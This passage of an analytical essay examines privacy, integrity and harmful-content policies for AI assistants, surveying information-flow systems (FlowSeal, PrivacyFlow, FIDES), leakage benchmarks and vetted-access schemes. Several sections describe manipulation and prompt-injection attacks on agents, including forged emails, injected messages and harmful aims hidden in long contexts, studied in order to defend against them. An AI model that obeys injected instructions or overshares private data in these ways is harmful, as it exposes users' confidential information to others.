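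Nissenbaum's original five parameters did not include purpose. Datta urged her to add a parameter for how the recipient will use the information, because privacy laws mention use so often, and by 2019 she was increasingly persuaded. *GoldCoin* (2024) applies the theory to language models. In its example of a doctor sending a patient's blood test results to a colleague, the formula includes the purpose, which is to plan treatment.

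The *Report on the NSF Workshop on Formal Methods for Security* (2016) notes that the 2006 work stated its norms in first-order logic, which can express rules about all people and all messages, but enforced only the propositional part, which has no variables for people or messages. Later logics covered every disclosure clause in HIPAA and in the equivalent US law for financial firms.

Even then, a program cannot tell from any log what a message was for. Datta and colleagues therefore let a condition be true, false or unknown. Their algorithm checks what the records can settle and leaves the rest of the norm to a human auditor. It can also run before an action and approve it, reject it or list the conditions that are still unknown. A harness could use that list to ask Ana one specific question instead of a general one.

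The formula works, however, only if the sender has already tagged the message correctly, which is the hard part. If the assistant tags "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" as health information, the health norm requires Ana's consent, but that norm doesn't apply if the assistant tags the sentence as a work schedule.

### A lattice around one person

Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) return to a lattice in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, but build it around a single data subject. Their system, FlowSeal, has three ordered levels, ⊥ ⊑ agent ⊑ ⊤. The subject's sensitive records are at the top, and outside destinations are at the bottom. The agent's context window moves to the middle level once the agent has read one of these records.

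Code outside the model intercepts every tool call that writes or shares something. It lets content *c* go to destination *d* only if

ℓ(c) ⊑ ℓ(d) or declassify(c, d) = SAFE,

where ℓ gives the level. The first condition fails for any outsider once the agent has read a sensitive record, so the second usually decides. The function *declassify* is a call to a separate language model that sees only the protected records and the proposed output. It must answer BLOCKED if the output reveals, confirms, denies or paraphrases anything in the records. The agent can then ask the data subject to approve the release of particular records to that recipient.

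The researchers tested FlowSeal against outsiders who manipulate an agent without prompt injection. One attack asks the agent to fill in its part of a shared document. Another asks it to delete the false records from a list about someone, which reveals that the remaining records are true. A third splits the request and the disclosure between email and a shared page. The table compares FlowSeal with a prompt that tells the agent to verify identities and get consent before it shares anything.

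| | Consent prompt | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Sensitive items leaked, shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Sensitive items leaked, list clean-up | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Sensitive items leaked, split channels | 43.8% | 2.2% |
| Harmless tasks completed | 44.7% | 72.4% |
| Sensitive items shared when the subject would consent | 66.6% | 32.7% |

None of the harmless tasks in the fourth row needed sensitive information, so FlowSeal's drawbacks barely show there. The last row is closer to Ana's second message, because sharing was the right outcome and the data subject would agree if asked. FlowSeal shared less than a third of what it should have there, mainly because its agents asked for consent less often.

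Shim and colleagues prove that information derived from a protected record can reach an outsider only if the checking model wrongly returns SAFE. The guarantee therefore depends on the model's accuracy, and paraphrases sometimes get past it. Still, an attacker can't send messages to the checker or prevent it from running. When the researchers replaced it with a rule that always returned SAFE, leakage in the shared-document attack rose to 24.9%. With a rule that always returned BLOCKED, no harmless tasks were completed.

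The check is also simpler than the norms it protects. It would block "Ana is away on Tuesday morning" because the sentence comes from the email, whether or not a manager ought to know. Ana could approve sharing the date alone only if someone had registered it separately from the diagnosis. The agent states a purpose when it asks for approval, but the release rule compares only content and destination.

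### Taking the privacy decision away from the task

FlowSeal leaves the final judgement to a model, though not the one doing the task. *Privacy Conductor* (Thornton, Pritom and colleagues, 2026) describes a system in which no model makes the decision. The system sits between an assistant and an organisation's documents. A person or body with authority writes a policy in advance, and a fixed program decides which documents the assistant may fetch for each requester. For example, the assistant may fetch a patient's record for a doctor only if the record's label permits the doctor's role and the doctor is assigned to that patient. The program never reads the request, so the wording of the request cannot change the result.

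The label has fields for the data subject, the permitted roles, the information type and the governing principle, and the sender is always the document store. On 2,520 combinations of requester and document from an invented clinic, the program reproduced the clinic's policy exactly, as expected of a fixed program. When language models wrote the labels, the seven set-ups chose the right sensitivity level for 78–86% of documents, but the worst reproduced the list of permitted roles for only 23%. When the same documents were labelled five times with an identical request, between 13 and 124 access decisions changed. On 214 flows from HIPAA court cases, the most accurate set-up judged 87.8% correctly but allowed 11 of the 20 disclosures that the law prohibits.

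Thornton and colleagues conclude that models can describe what a document contains but can't decide who should receive it. Using models only to label documents still leaves Ana with a problem. Each label covers a whole document, so the date and the diagnosis stay together. Privacy Conductor also gives an assistant the same access as the person it works for, so Ana's assistant can read all her email. The system would protect her records from other people's assistants, but it doesn't control what her own assistant writes to her manager.

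In *PrivacyFlow*, Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues (2026) take nearly the opposite approach. They argue that no rule written in advance can cover every combination of circumstances, so they have a model reason about privacy before the agent acts. The model drafts a plan, notes where each piece of data came from and why each recipient would get it, and simulates what the recipient could infer by combining it with what they already know. The system then either carries out a version of the plan that shares less, blocks the plan, or consults the user. In principle, the simulation could detect that Tuesday's date reveals Ana's diagnosis, which a check for copied content would miss.

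The same researchers built PrivacyBench, a set of 986 sequences of about six office tasks each. Each sensitive fact has a list of the people who may know it, so reader sets apply to facts instead of documents. The agent never sees the lists and has to infer from the surrounding messages who should know what. Without PrivacyFlow, six models avoided any privacy failure in only 13.0–52.9% of the sequences. PrivacyFlow raised that share by 22 to 55 percentage points, and the agents kept most of their success at the tasks. A prompt telling the agent to respect privacy changed the pass rate for individual steps by at most 3.2 points.

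PrivacyFlow completed more authorised tasks when it could ask the user about cases it was unsure of, but this handed decisions back to the user. It also relies on a model's judgement and has no equivalent of FlowSeal's proof. PrivacyFlow addresses the question Ana cares about, but its answers are less certain than those Privacy Conductor gives to a coarser question.

### Oversharing with no attacker

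Agents disclose too much even when nobody is trying to trick them. In a pilot study by Staab and colleagues, an agent scheduling a dismissal meeting told the employee about a covert investigation into them. The pilot found 87 privacy failures in 240 steps. In 67 of those failures the agent had done what the user asked, so a user who checked only whether the task was done would not notice them.

*Capable but Careless* (Goel and Gurevych, 2026) measured this with AgentCIBench, which puts an agent in charge of a person's messenger, calendar, to-do list and other apps. Each of its 117 scenarios has a task, a recipient, items the agent must share and items it must not. In one, a user asks the agent to send a colleague the list of office supplies, which are on the same shopping list as personal purchases.

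Twelve of 15 agents leaked something in more than half of the scenarios. On average, agents shared all the required items in 68.8% of scenarios and leaked in 67.9%. How often an agent shared the required items was a poor predictor of how often it leaked. Claude Opus 4.7 shared them in 81.2% of scenarios and leaked in 13.7%, while Gemini 3.1 Pro shared them in 96.6% and leaked in 98.3%. Another model leaked in only 18.8%, but it refused 41.9% of the tasks and shared the required items in 44.4%.

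These rates overstate what an ordinary user would see, because a search procedure selected scenarios that had already made other models leak. Goel and Gurevych therefore use them to compare agents. They also tried three simple countermeasures, which cut leakage on attempted tasks by 33 to 36 percentage points and raised task success.

Newer models do somewhat better at best. Guo, Chen and colleagues (2026) built AgentCIScope, a set of 936 tasks across 11 applications, and ran 12 combinations of model and agent software on it. Leakage ranged from 32.5% of tasks for Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code to 94.4% for Gemini 3.8 Flash in Google's agent toolkit. The same model's leakage rate could differ by more than 10 percentage points depending on the agent software. Repeating each task five times raised the share with at least one leak by 4 to 19 points, which matters for an assistant that does similar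 jobs every week. The tasks are a stress test, because the researchers reworded the instructions to encourage oversharing without asking for it, for example by requesting a briefing that makes sense on its own.

The agents protected information that looks secret much better than information that is private only in context. They leaked credit card details 17.1% of the time and US social security numbers 29.4%, but booking details 76.5% and personal preferences 84.7%. They leaked more from the calendar than from any other source, and they tend to give away details like Ana's appointment.

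To decide what counts as a leak, Guo and colleagues started with a fixed list of 39 sensitive types of information. A language model then judged each case in the role of a strict, a moderate and a relaxed person, and the researchers kept an item only if all three objected to sharing it. Another check compared the flow of information with the text of a privacy policy. These filters make the remaining violations fairly clear-cut, although one model played all three people. They also remove the cases on which reasonable people disagree, so we learn little from the results about how agents handle them.

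### When no norm is settled

The main objection to using contextual integrity for agents comes from those harder cases. The theory judges a flow by the norms of its context, but an agent may work in many contexts at once and create flows nobody has seen before. *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI* (Jenkins, Kitkowska and colleagues, 2026) reports on a workshop of 30 experts who disagreed about what to do. Some wanted to discard the theory because there are not yet well-defined norms to reason about.

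In one of the workshop's examples, an agent gives the user's address to a restaurant while trying to make a booking. The booking fails and the agent moves on to a second restaurant, but the first still has the address of someone who isn't its customer. There is no established norm for an agent that shares a person's details with ten businesses in a minute, although people have long given their details to businesses themselves.

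Agents may also change the norms they are supposed to follow. *Got a Secret?* (2026) found that, in communities of agents, an agent becomes more likely to share sensitive details after seeing other agents share theirs. An agent that learns what is appropriate from its surroundings can therefore learn the wrong norms even if nobody deliberately misleads it.

Others at the workshop replied that the theory's basic idea is sound and that only the rules for applying it need to change. Nissenbaum's account supports them. She presumes in favour of established norms but doesn't treat them as final. An evaluator of a new kind of flow identifies its five parameters, then considers whose interests the flow affects, which ethical and political values are at stake, and whether the flow serves the purposes of the context. Her original method compared the new practice with an older one, but by 2019 she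 had concluded that the method could work without a precedent, because so many new flows had none.

This reply seems right for most of what Ana's assistant does. Using software to write to her manager doesn't change their roles or what employees owe their employers. But the assistant has no way to keep the norm attached to the information as it moves between contexts. *Beyond Disclosure* (2026) describes an assistant that remembers medical details from a request for health advice and later uses them in a professional setting. The assistant obtained the details legitimately but violated the norm by moving them to a new context. The paper proposes that memory systems store the constraints of the original context and enforce them at retrieval, instead of fetching whatever seems relevant.

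The reply is weaker when the recipient is another agent or the information flow has no familiar counterpart. Nissenbaum's method can guide a committee that has weeks to consider a new practice, but a harness has to decide before the next tool call. Someone must already have turned the committee's conclusion into a rule, and the theory doesn't specify who. Even established law leaves such gaps. Thornton and colleagues point out that HIPAA may limit who can open a clinical record without necessarily specifying which nurse in a clinic may open a particular patient's.

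## Harmful-content rules, which have no source to label

Privacy norms protect the person the information is about, but rules against harmful content also restrict information that isn't about anyone, such as the dose at which a medicine becomes dangerous. Suppose Ana looks after her father and, to keep him safe, asks her assistant how many of his tablets would be too many. Someone considering an overdose could ask the same question, and the answer could help them take one.

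### An answer that arrives without a label

The model reads only the operator's instructions and Ana's question before it answers. Under FIDES's defaults both are trusted and public, so the answer is too, and it may go to anyone. The dose has no tag because it came from the model's weights, the numbers that store what it learned in training, and not from a document in the context window.

Labelling the model's weights as a whole doesn't help, because every answer depends on them and a single label would block either all answers or none. If the assistant looked up a dose on a clinic's web page, the answer would have a source, but its label would only record who wrote the page and who may read it, neither of which affects how dangerous the answer is.

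Contextual integrity comes closer because it takes account of the recipient. But the deciding fact is now something about the recipient, and the assistant usually has only the recipient's word for it. If Ana types that she is a carer, FIDES treats her message as trusted, which makes sense when the threat is a stranger giving orders. A harmful-content filter can't rely on that message, because the person whose access is in doubt wrote it. (In effect, the user changes sides between the two policies.)

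Roy Chowdhury and Garimella (2026), in *How Safe Is ChatGPT Health Advice?*, measured how much the safety of a response depends on who is asking. They collected the full ChatGPT histories of 1,252 people in India, Nigeria, Brazil and Pakistan and found 15,555 conversations about health. A language model scored the safety of each conversation's responses twice, first in isolation and then with a profile of what the user had revealed in earlier conversations. In isolation, 20.6% to 26.3% of conversations were rated high-risk, depending on the country, and dangerous advice on medicines or doses was a recurring fault. With the profile, the share rose by 13 to 17 percentage points. About one in four conversations rated safe in isolation were rated unsafe with the profile. Fitness advice was among the safest categories in isolation but among the riskiest when the scoring took the user's medical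 conditions into account.

The judge was not a clinician, so these scores measure risk, not actual injuries. The users were paid volunteers, not a representative sample of their countries. The result points in the same direction as earlier work on invented users. *Safe for Whom?* (2025) describes two cases in which advice scored 5 out of 7 for a generic user but 2 or 3 for a particular vulnerable user.

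Carers like Ana make up a small but regular share of people asking about health. In Nigeria, 11% of women's health conversations were about a dependant, compared with 1% of men's. In India, the figure was 3% for both women and men. A filter built on the assumption that people always ask about themselves would misclassify these requests.

Roy Chowdhury and Garimella note that the information needed to avoid most of the harms was already in the conversation history. A filter could use that information, but only by reading some of the most private data the assistant holds. A refusal might also reveal part of that data to anyone who shares the account.

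### Measuring what the requester learns

Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2024), in *Breach By A Thousand Leaks*, propose measuring the change in what the requester believes, so the answer needs no label. Let *p* be the probability the requester gives to the forbidden answer before talking to the model, and *p′* the probability afterwards. The impermissible information leakage is

leakage = *p′* × log(*p′* / *p*).

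The unit is the nat because the logarithms are natural. The first two rows below use pairs of beliefs from the paper's motivation for its definition. The third row is an added example of someone who already nearly knew the answer, such as a pharmacist.

| Belief before | Belief after | log(*p′* / *p*) | Leakage in nats |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1 | 0.9 | 2.20 | 1.98 |
| 0.001 | 0.009 | 2.20 | 0.02 |
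| 0.9 | 0.95 | 0.05 | 0.05 |

Belief rises ninefold in both of the first two rows, so they would be equally serious by the logarithm alone. But the first requester ends up fairly sure of the answer, while the second still gives it less than a 1% chance. Multiplying by the later belief makes the first case a hundred times as serious. The third requester ends up the most certain, but the model contributed little to that certainty.

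Unlike labels, the definition therefore accounts for what requesters already know, but it still doesn't account for why they want the answer. If Ana and a person at risk start with the same belief about the dose and read the same reply, the leakage is the same for both.

When a question has several possible answers, the measure adds up the leakage for only the forbidden ones. It doesn't count leakage when a requester becomes certain of a harmless answer. Mutual information, the standard measure of what one variable reveals about another, would count that too. The measure also covers everything the requester has received, because answers that are acceptable separately can together reveal a forbidden one.

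### Refusing at random

A company could use this measure to set a limit, written ε, on the leakage that any question may cause on average. Glukhov and colleagues give a simple mechanism that stays within the limit. It returns the model's real answer with probability *t* and otherwise returns a safe reply, such as an empty one. Let *L* be the largest expected leakage that any single question could cause if the model always answered, taking the worst case over all the requesters under consideration. Then

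*t* = min(ε / *L*, 1).

An empty reply leaks nothing because it doesn't change anyone's belief in a forbidden answer. Leakage occurs only in the fraction *t* of cases where the model answers, so the expected leakage is at most *t* × *L*, which is at most ε.

Suppose the worst case is the rise from 0.1 to 0.9, so *L* is 1.98, and the company sets ε at 0.1. Then *t* is about 0.05, and Ana gets an answer about one time in 20. But she or anyone else could ask again. The limits for separate questions add up (with a further term if the replies depend on one another), so to keep the total for ten questions to 0.1, the company can allow only 0.01 for each. The model would then answer about one time in 200.

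If an empty reply is worth nothing to an honest user, the expected usefulness falls to exactly *t* times what it was. That is a poor bargain, and a less crude mechanism might be expected to do better. A second theorem limits what any mechanism can achieve if it keeps leakage below ε:

what the honest user learns ≤ ε + *H* + *R*.

*H* is the uncertainty that someone who knew the answer to the forbidden question would still have about the honest user's question. *R* is how much the reply reveals about permitted answers to the forbidden question. The inequality must hold for every forbidden question and every adversary considered, so the smallest value of *H* + *R* sets the limit.

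The argument has three steps:

1. What a reply reveals about the honest question can't exceed what it reveals about the honest and forbidden questions together.
2. That total splits into what the reply reveals about the forbidden question, and what it adds about the honest question for someone who already knows the forbidden answer.
3. The first part is at most ε + *R*, because the mechanism caps leakage about forbidden answers at ε. The second part is at most *H*, since nobody can learn more about a question than they were uncertain of.

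If Ana asks what time of day her father should take his tablets, *H* is large, because someone who knows the dangerous dose still doesn't know the timetable. The bound then allows a full answer. But if she asks for the dangerous dose, her question is the forbidden one and *H* is zero. The permitted answers are the wrong doses, so beyond ε she could learn only about those.

It would be hard to run a real filter this way, because someone would have to list the forbidden questions and their answers and estimate what every possible adversary believes. Glukhov and colleagues measured leakage on multiple-choice questions, where each question has one correct option and a language model's probabilities can stand in for beliefs. Open conversation lacks this structure. The theorem is more useful as a limit on what filters can do, and it assumes the mechanism sees only the question. A system that could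 reliably tell Ana from a person at risk could give the answer to only one of them.

### Aims that a model has to infer

Deployed assistants judge each request instead of refusing at random, which works only if they recognise a harmful aim. *Do Reasoning LLMs Refuse What They Infer in Long Contexts?* (Fu, Shahgir and colleagues, 2026) tested 15 models on 100 harmful requests. In one version, the text contained the request word for word. In the others, several passages together implied it but none stated it in full. Every version ended with a neutral instruction. The table gives the average share of responses that did not fulfil the harmful aim.

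| Unrelated text added | Aim stated | Aim inferred |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 55% |
| Up to 16,000 tokens | 96% | 43% |
| Up to 64,000 tokens | 95% | 42% |

The scoring was lenient, because a response counted as unsafe only if it received the worst of five grades. Results also varied widely between models. When the texts were longest and the aim had to be inferred, GPT-5.2 was safe in 75% to 82% of cases and Gemini 3 Flash in 2% to 14%, depending on how the passages fitted together. OpenAI and Google have both released newer models since.

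The models could piece together the scattered aims but often didn't treat harmful ones as something to refuse. When Fu and colleagues scattered harmless aims through text in the same way, GPT-oss-20b, a small open model from OpenAI, worked out 95% to 100% of them. More reasoning helped the larger GPT-oss-120b, whose average share of safe responses rose from 27.0% at low effort to 64.6% at medium and 80.4% at high, although the reasoning at high effort was more than twice as long as at medium.

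Extra safety training also helped, but with a tradeoff similar to the one in the theorem. One method raised a small model's rate of safe responses from 34.2% to 82.3% when the aim had to be inferred. On a separate test, it also raised the share of harmless requests that the model refused from 1.6% to 41.2%.

Labels would not have caught any of this, just as they missed what the two remarks at the priest's party revealed together.

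### Clearance for people

Since the content has no label and the model's judgement is unreliable, a company can check who is asking. Military systems have always done this by giving people clearances. Axios' *OpenAI opens powerful cyber tools to verified users* (2026) described OpenAI's April plan as a shift from restricting what models can do to verifying who gets the most sensitive capabilities.

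The resulting scheme, called Daybreak, has three tiers. Higher tiers get fewer refusals on security work, and the tier needed depends on the model. OpenAI lists the terms for each one, including these three:

| Model | Standard | Daybreak Blue | Daybreak Red |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Sol | standard safeguards | fewer refusals | fewer refusals |
| GPT-6.2 Astra | standard safeguards | standard safeguards | fewer refusals |
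| GPT-6 Cyber | no access | no access | fewer refusals, after separate approval |

Individuals can apply for Blue, but normally only organisations can get Red. Reviewers consider the applicant's identity, the intended use, the risk and whether the applicant can strengthen security for others. After approval, an administrator still has to enable Daybreak for particular people or projects, and it has to be active for the request. Similarly, a military clearance alone doesn't entitle anyone to a file they have no need to see.

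The requirements for biology look even more like a security clearance. OpenAI's *Request Trusted Access for Biology Research* requires a verifiable identity and affiliation, and a research purpose that fits the institution's mission. The terms also cover controls against insider threats, such as background checks where appropriate and regular access reviews, and the institution must report suspected misuse within 24 hours. OpenAI concedes in its *Life Science Research Special Access Program* that its standard safeguards can create "high friction" for some researchers doing beneficial work.

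According to Anthropic's *Claude Mythos 5.2*, the same underlying model is used on both sides of the boundary, as Claude Mythos 5.2 and Claude Fable 5.2. Anyone can use Fable, which has safeguards that block or limit it in risky areas, while only vetted organisations can use Mythos. On one benchmark of scientific research tasks, Fable scored 74.6% and Mythos 75.3%, and Anthropic attributes such gaps to tasks where the safeguards intervene. The loss of usefulness is small, though most scientific tasks are presumably far from the forbidden material.

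These clearances don't form a single ranking. The Decoder's *Anthropic releases Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5* reported a plan to give selected researchers a version of Fable 5 without the biology and chemistry safeguards but with the cyber ones. A biologist's clearance and a security tester's are then incomparable, like the labels *medical* and *financial* in Denning's example.

Vetting works best for institutions with a recognisable professional need. It does little for Ana, because no company will check that her father takes heart medicine, and she needs the answer tonight. Vetting a person also doesn't cover what their agent reads. OpenAI bars customers from using Daybreak for outside users or customer-facing products, which limits who can send text to a model with fewer refusals. But an approved tester's agent may still open a stranger's web page, and a prompt injection on that page would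 reach the model with the tester's privileges.

### Taking the material out of training

A company cannot vet users once it publishes a model's weights, because anyone can download them and nobody can recall them. The developer can instead try to keep the model from learning the dangerous material. The Chinese company Moonshot AI did this with Kimi K3.1 Pro, released in October 2026.

Maier (2026), in *Kimi K3.1 Pro*, explains how. Moonshot had noticed that the model's ability to exploit software flaws kept growing during training, although nobody had set out to teach it hacking. The company traced the skill to security material in its general training data and to security tasks in reinforcement learning, the stage at which a model practises tasks and gets rewards. It removed both and kept the ordinary coding tasks. Moonshot then compared two versions on its own test of exploiting real flaws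 in software such as the Linux kernel. Constantin (2026), in *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills*, reports the scores:

| Model | Tasks solved |
|---|---|
| Kimi K3, the predecessor | 33.3% |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro, trained without the cuts | 90.5% |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro, as released | 81% |
| DeepSeek V4.1-Flash, a rival open model | 85.7% |

Removing the material caused the fall from 90.5% to 81%, which undid about a sixth of the improvement over Kimi K3. One reason the rest survived may be that the model is a further-trained version of Kimi K3, according to Moonshot AI's *Kimi K3.1 Pro Tech Blog*, so cuts in the later training would not erase what the older model already knew. Another may be that skill at finding flaws overlaps with skill at programming. SecurityWeek reported a similar experience at Anthropic, which avoided training Claude Opus 5 directly on offensive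 hacking tasks but still saw some gains from general improvement. A developer can label a document as hacking material and leave it out, but the model may work out much of its content from the documents that remain.

Removing dangerous training data also involves a trade-off between safety and usefulness. *Beyond Data Filtering* (2025) notes that a filter either leaves some dangerous content in or throws out data that the model needs for other things. Every user also loses the removed material, whatever their purpose. *Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering* (2026) therefore suggests combining removal with clearance for models whose weights stay private. The public would get the filtered version and vetted users the full one.

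Training a separate model for each kind of user would be very expensive. *Modular Pretraining Enables Access Control* (Roland, Cubuktepe et al., 2026) describes a method called GRAM that produces several versions of a model from one training run. It adds a small module to the network for each sensitive subject and labels the training data by subject. When the network trains on virology papers, for example, the virology module always learns from them, while the shared part of the network learns from them only some of the time. Knowledge of virology therefore tends to collect in its module, which the developer can later switch off for users who aren't cleared for that subject.

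This comes closest to labeling the weights. A user's permissions are a set of subjects, and the possible sets form the same kind of lattice as Denning's records.

The researchers trained a model with 800 million parameters (the numbers that make up its weights) on general text and four specialized subjects: virology, cybersecurity, nuclear physics and a rare programming language. GRAM kept and removed subjects about as well as training separate models on filtered data, and it did far better than filtering when only part of the data had labels. Retraining a model to recover the knowledge in a switched-off module was about as hard as teaching that knowledge to a model that had never seen it. The test assumed an attacker with little data, and Roland and colleagues expect that anyone with much more could partly recover the knowledge. The largest model they trained had 5 billion parameters, while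 Kimi K3 has nearly 3 trillion.

They also measured how well a model predicts text on a subject, not whether it can carry out a dangerous task. Moonshot's result raises the question of how much hacking skill would remain in the shared part of a very large model that had learned to program.

Even a perfect version would divide the information in the wrong place for Ana. Dangerous doses appear in the same medical texts as safe ones, so a module that held the dangerous doses would probably also hold much of what a carer needs. She would get no answer with the module off, and someone would have to establish that she is a carer before switching it on for her.

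## Combining policies that share no ranking

Each policy defines its own high and low sides for the same agent, so two policies can reasonably treat the same person differently. For example, an assistant's harmful-content filter may treat Ana as a possible risk when she asks about her father's medication, while its privacy rules protect her when it writes to her manager.

### One agent, three pairs of sides

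| | Privacy | Integrity | Harmful content |
|---|---|---|---|
| Protects | personal information | the agent's actions and trusted stores | people whom dangerous knowledge could hurt |
| Against | recipients not entitled to it | authors of untrusted text | whoever is asking |
| Checks data going | out of the context window to a recipient | from text the agent has read into an action or a store | out of the model to the user |
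| Ana's side | high | high | low |

The clinic's side also varies. For confidentiality, it is on the high side for its own email, which it may read, but on the low side for Ana's calendar. For integrity, it is on the low side for everything it sends.

The three policies also need checks in different places. FIDES checks its policies only before tool calls, because it normally treats a reply to the user as having no consequences. This works for privacy and integrity, since Ana may read everything in her own assistant's context window and a reply to her changes nothing outside it. But a harmful answer would reach her in the reply, which FIDES doesn't normally check. Costa and colleagues say that a harness can check every step the model proposes, including replies, where this matters.

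Privacy and integrity policies can share one system of labels, but a harmful-content rule has no label to compare, so it can only add a yes-or-no decision from a filter.

### Labels that neither rank above nor equal each other

The labels of Ana's calendar and the clinic's web page are incomparable, since neither ranks above the other. Text from the calendar is secret, so it can't go onto a public page, and text from the web page can't go into a trusted calendar, because a stranger could have written it. Incomparable labels block data in both directions, unlike equal labels, which let it move freely.

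When labels are incomparable, a piece of text may have no single best label. Suppose Ana asks whether the clinic is closed on Monday, and both a note in her calendar and the clinic's web page give the answer. An answer based on the calendar is secret and trusted, and the same answer based on the web page is public and untrusted. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, look for the least restrictive label that an output can have. They note that there may be several, and say the system should find them all and let the application choose. Here the assistant could choose the public label to tell a friend the answer, or the trusted label if it is about to cancel a taxi because of the answer.

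A single ranking for both secrecy and integrity cannot represent such cases, because the two classical rules together let data move only within a level. Sandhu (1993), in *Lattice-Based Access Control Models*, equates this with a policy of isolated classes, in which nothing flows from one class to another. Such a policy breaks Denning's conditions for a lattice because it has no bottom label whose data may flow anywhere and no join for two different labels. A message made from two levels of data would therefore have no label.

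With a separate label for each property, the contradiction disappears. Sandhu calls this the composite model and reports that several operating systems, databases and network products built for the military used it. Applied to a session of Ana's assistant, its rules give these permissions:

| Session's label | May read | May write to |
|---|---|---|
| public, trusted | operator's instructions | any place |
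| secret, trusted | instructions, calendar | secret places |
| public, untrusted | instructions, web page | untrusted places |
| secret, untrusted | all four items | places that are both secret and untrusted |

A session that is allowed to read more data is allowed to write to fewer places. An assistant that has read all four items could save notes in a private scratch file but do little else. Separate labels make the rules consistent with each other, but they don't make mixed data easier to use.

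Sandhu explains how people with clearances get round this. Someone cleared for Secret who wants to write an Unclassified document logs in again at the Unclassified level, where the software can't open Secret files. A harness could likewise start a fresh session with only the instructions and the calendar, and send Ana's manager the message about Thursday from there. It couldn't send the message about her absence from that session, because the date is in the email.

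Real systems therefore need exceptions as well as separate labels. Sandhu describes a design by Lipner for an ordinary data-processing department, with integrity and secrecy labels that could combine in 192 ways. Lipner used only nine of them but still had to let the system control staff write down.

### Requiring both checks or either one

FIDES builds its exceptions from two policies. Each tool call has a label ℓ<sub>f</sub> for the decision to make the call and labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ for its arguments. Each label has an integrity part, T (trusted) or U (untrusted), and a set of permitted readers.

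1. **Trusted action.** A consequential call may run only if ℓ<sub>f</sub> ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ = (T, any readers). The symbol ⊔ is the join, so one untrusted part makes the whole call untrusted.
2. **Permitted readers.** A call may send an argument with reader set S through a channel only if R ⊆ S, where R is the set of people who can read the channel.

The message telling Ana's manager that she is away on Tuesday fails the second policy because the manager is in R but is not among the readers of the clinic's email. The email is also untrusted, so the message fails the first policy too. FIDES would therefore block it whether it required messages to pass both policies or just one.

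The version that Costa and colleagues tested is more lenient because it checks only whether the decision to make the call was trusted and ignores the labels of the arguments. Suppose Ana's own request leads the assistant to write to her manager, and a separate model fills in the date, so the email never reaches the model that chose the call. The decision is then trusted although the date isn't. The table shows what happens to this message and three others.

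| Message | Trusted decision? | Permitted readers? | Both required | Either enough |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| To the manager: free on Thursday, from the calendar | yes | yes | sent | sent |
| To the manager: away on Tuesday, date filled in from the email | yes | no | blocked | sent |
| To the manager: the clinic's opening hours, after reading its web page | no | yes | blocked | sent |
| To a stranger: the clinic's email, because the web page said to send it | no | no | blocked | blocked |

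Requiring a message to satisfy both policies gives the strongest guarantee but blocks two messages Ana might well want to send. Requiring it to satisfy either policy lets those two messages through and still stops the theft.

However, the lenient rule would allow an invented resignation letter as well as the opening hours. If a prompt injection on the web page made the assistant tell Ana's manager that she was leaving, the message would go out because it would contain nothing the manager may not read. Costa and colleagues saw milder cases of this in AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks with planted attacks. Their policies stopped every attack they counted as a real injection, but they didn't count an injected message that told a chat channel only what its members could already read, because the policy allowed it. They also banned sending untrusted links, since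 opening a link can send data to an outside server.

Each tool has its own rule. Of the 27 tools, 21 need only a trusted decision, including those for sending money, sharing a file and posting a web page. Five accept either check, including those for sending email and chat messages. Only the tool for adding people to a calendar event requires both, perhaps because it changes the event and shows it to new readers.

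This choice has a large effect on what an agent can do. With OpenAI's o1, the more capable of the two models tested, a simple agent that keeps everything in one context window completed these shares of the tasks when nobody was attacking it:

| Tasks | No policies | With policies |
|---|---|---|
| Office | 70.0% | 48.0% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% |
| Chat | 87.6% | 17.1% |

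Travel tasks were affected least because many of them use tools that may run after the agent has read untrusted text, as long as no secret goes to the wrong reader. Payments have no such exception, so an agent that has read even one untrusted file can't make them. The older GPT-4o also scored 37.5% on banking with policies in place, so a better model alone doesn't remove this limit.

### Exceptions that an attacker can't steer

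Sending the date to Ana's manager is a declassification. Costa and colleagues describe their lenient rule as a form of robust declassification. The full requirement, stated in *A Calculus for Flow-Limited Authorization* (2021), is that attackers can influence neither the decision to disclose nor the choice of what to disclose.

*Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, 2017) explains the idea in terms of what an attacker learns. If the attacker learns nothing about a secret from one attack, no other attack may reveal it either. All attacks are then equally effective, so the attacker can't control what is released. Testing this takes four runs of a program, one for each combination of two possible secrets and two attacks. *The Duality of Information Flow* (2026) reduces this to two runs by having programmers mark explicitly where robustness applies. In an agent's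 harness, tool calls are natural places for these marks, since anything the agent sends out has to go through one.

The version of FIDES that ignores the labels of arguments meets only half of the requirement. An attacker can't make the assistant write to Ana's manager, but can still affect what it writes. For example, an attacker could forge an email instructing the model that fills in the date to return everything it has read, and the manager would receive Ana's diagnosis instead of a date. The first policy as originally written covers arguments and would prevent this, but it would also block the honest message.

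One solution is to endorse the date for this one use. But endorsement has its own dangers, which Cecchetti and colleagues illustrate with a sealed-bid auction. Alice sends her secret bid to an auctioneer. Bob can't read it, but he can make his own bid by taking Alice's sealed bid and adding one. The auctioneer endorses Bob's bid as genuinely his, opens both, and Bob wins by the smallest possible margin. Their rule, transparent endorsement, forbids endorsing information that its provider could not have read, which rules out Bob's bid because he built it from a bid he couldn't see.

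Separate secrecy and integrity labels are enough for ordinary flows. Every exception has to take account of both properties, because robust declassification makes secrecy depend on integrity and transparent endorsement makes integrity depend on secrecy.

*Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* (2025) describes safe labels as those where anyone who can influence the data can also read it. When labels are expressed as sets of readers and writers, the test is simply whether every possible writer is also a reader.

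| Text | Possible writers | Readers | Passes? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calendar | Ana | Ana, manager | yes |
| Clinic's email | clinic | Ana, clinic | yes |
| Clinic's web page | clinic | everyone | yes |
| Calendar and web page together | Ana, clinic | Ana, manager | no |
| Calendar and email together | Ana, clinic | Ana | no |

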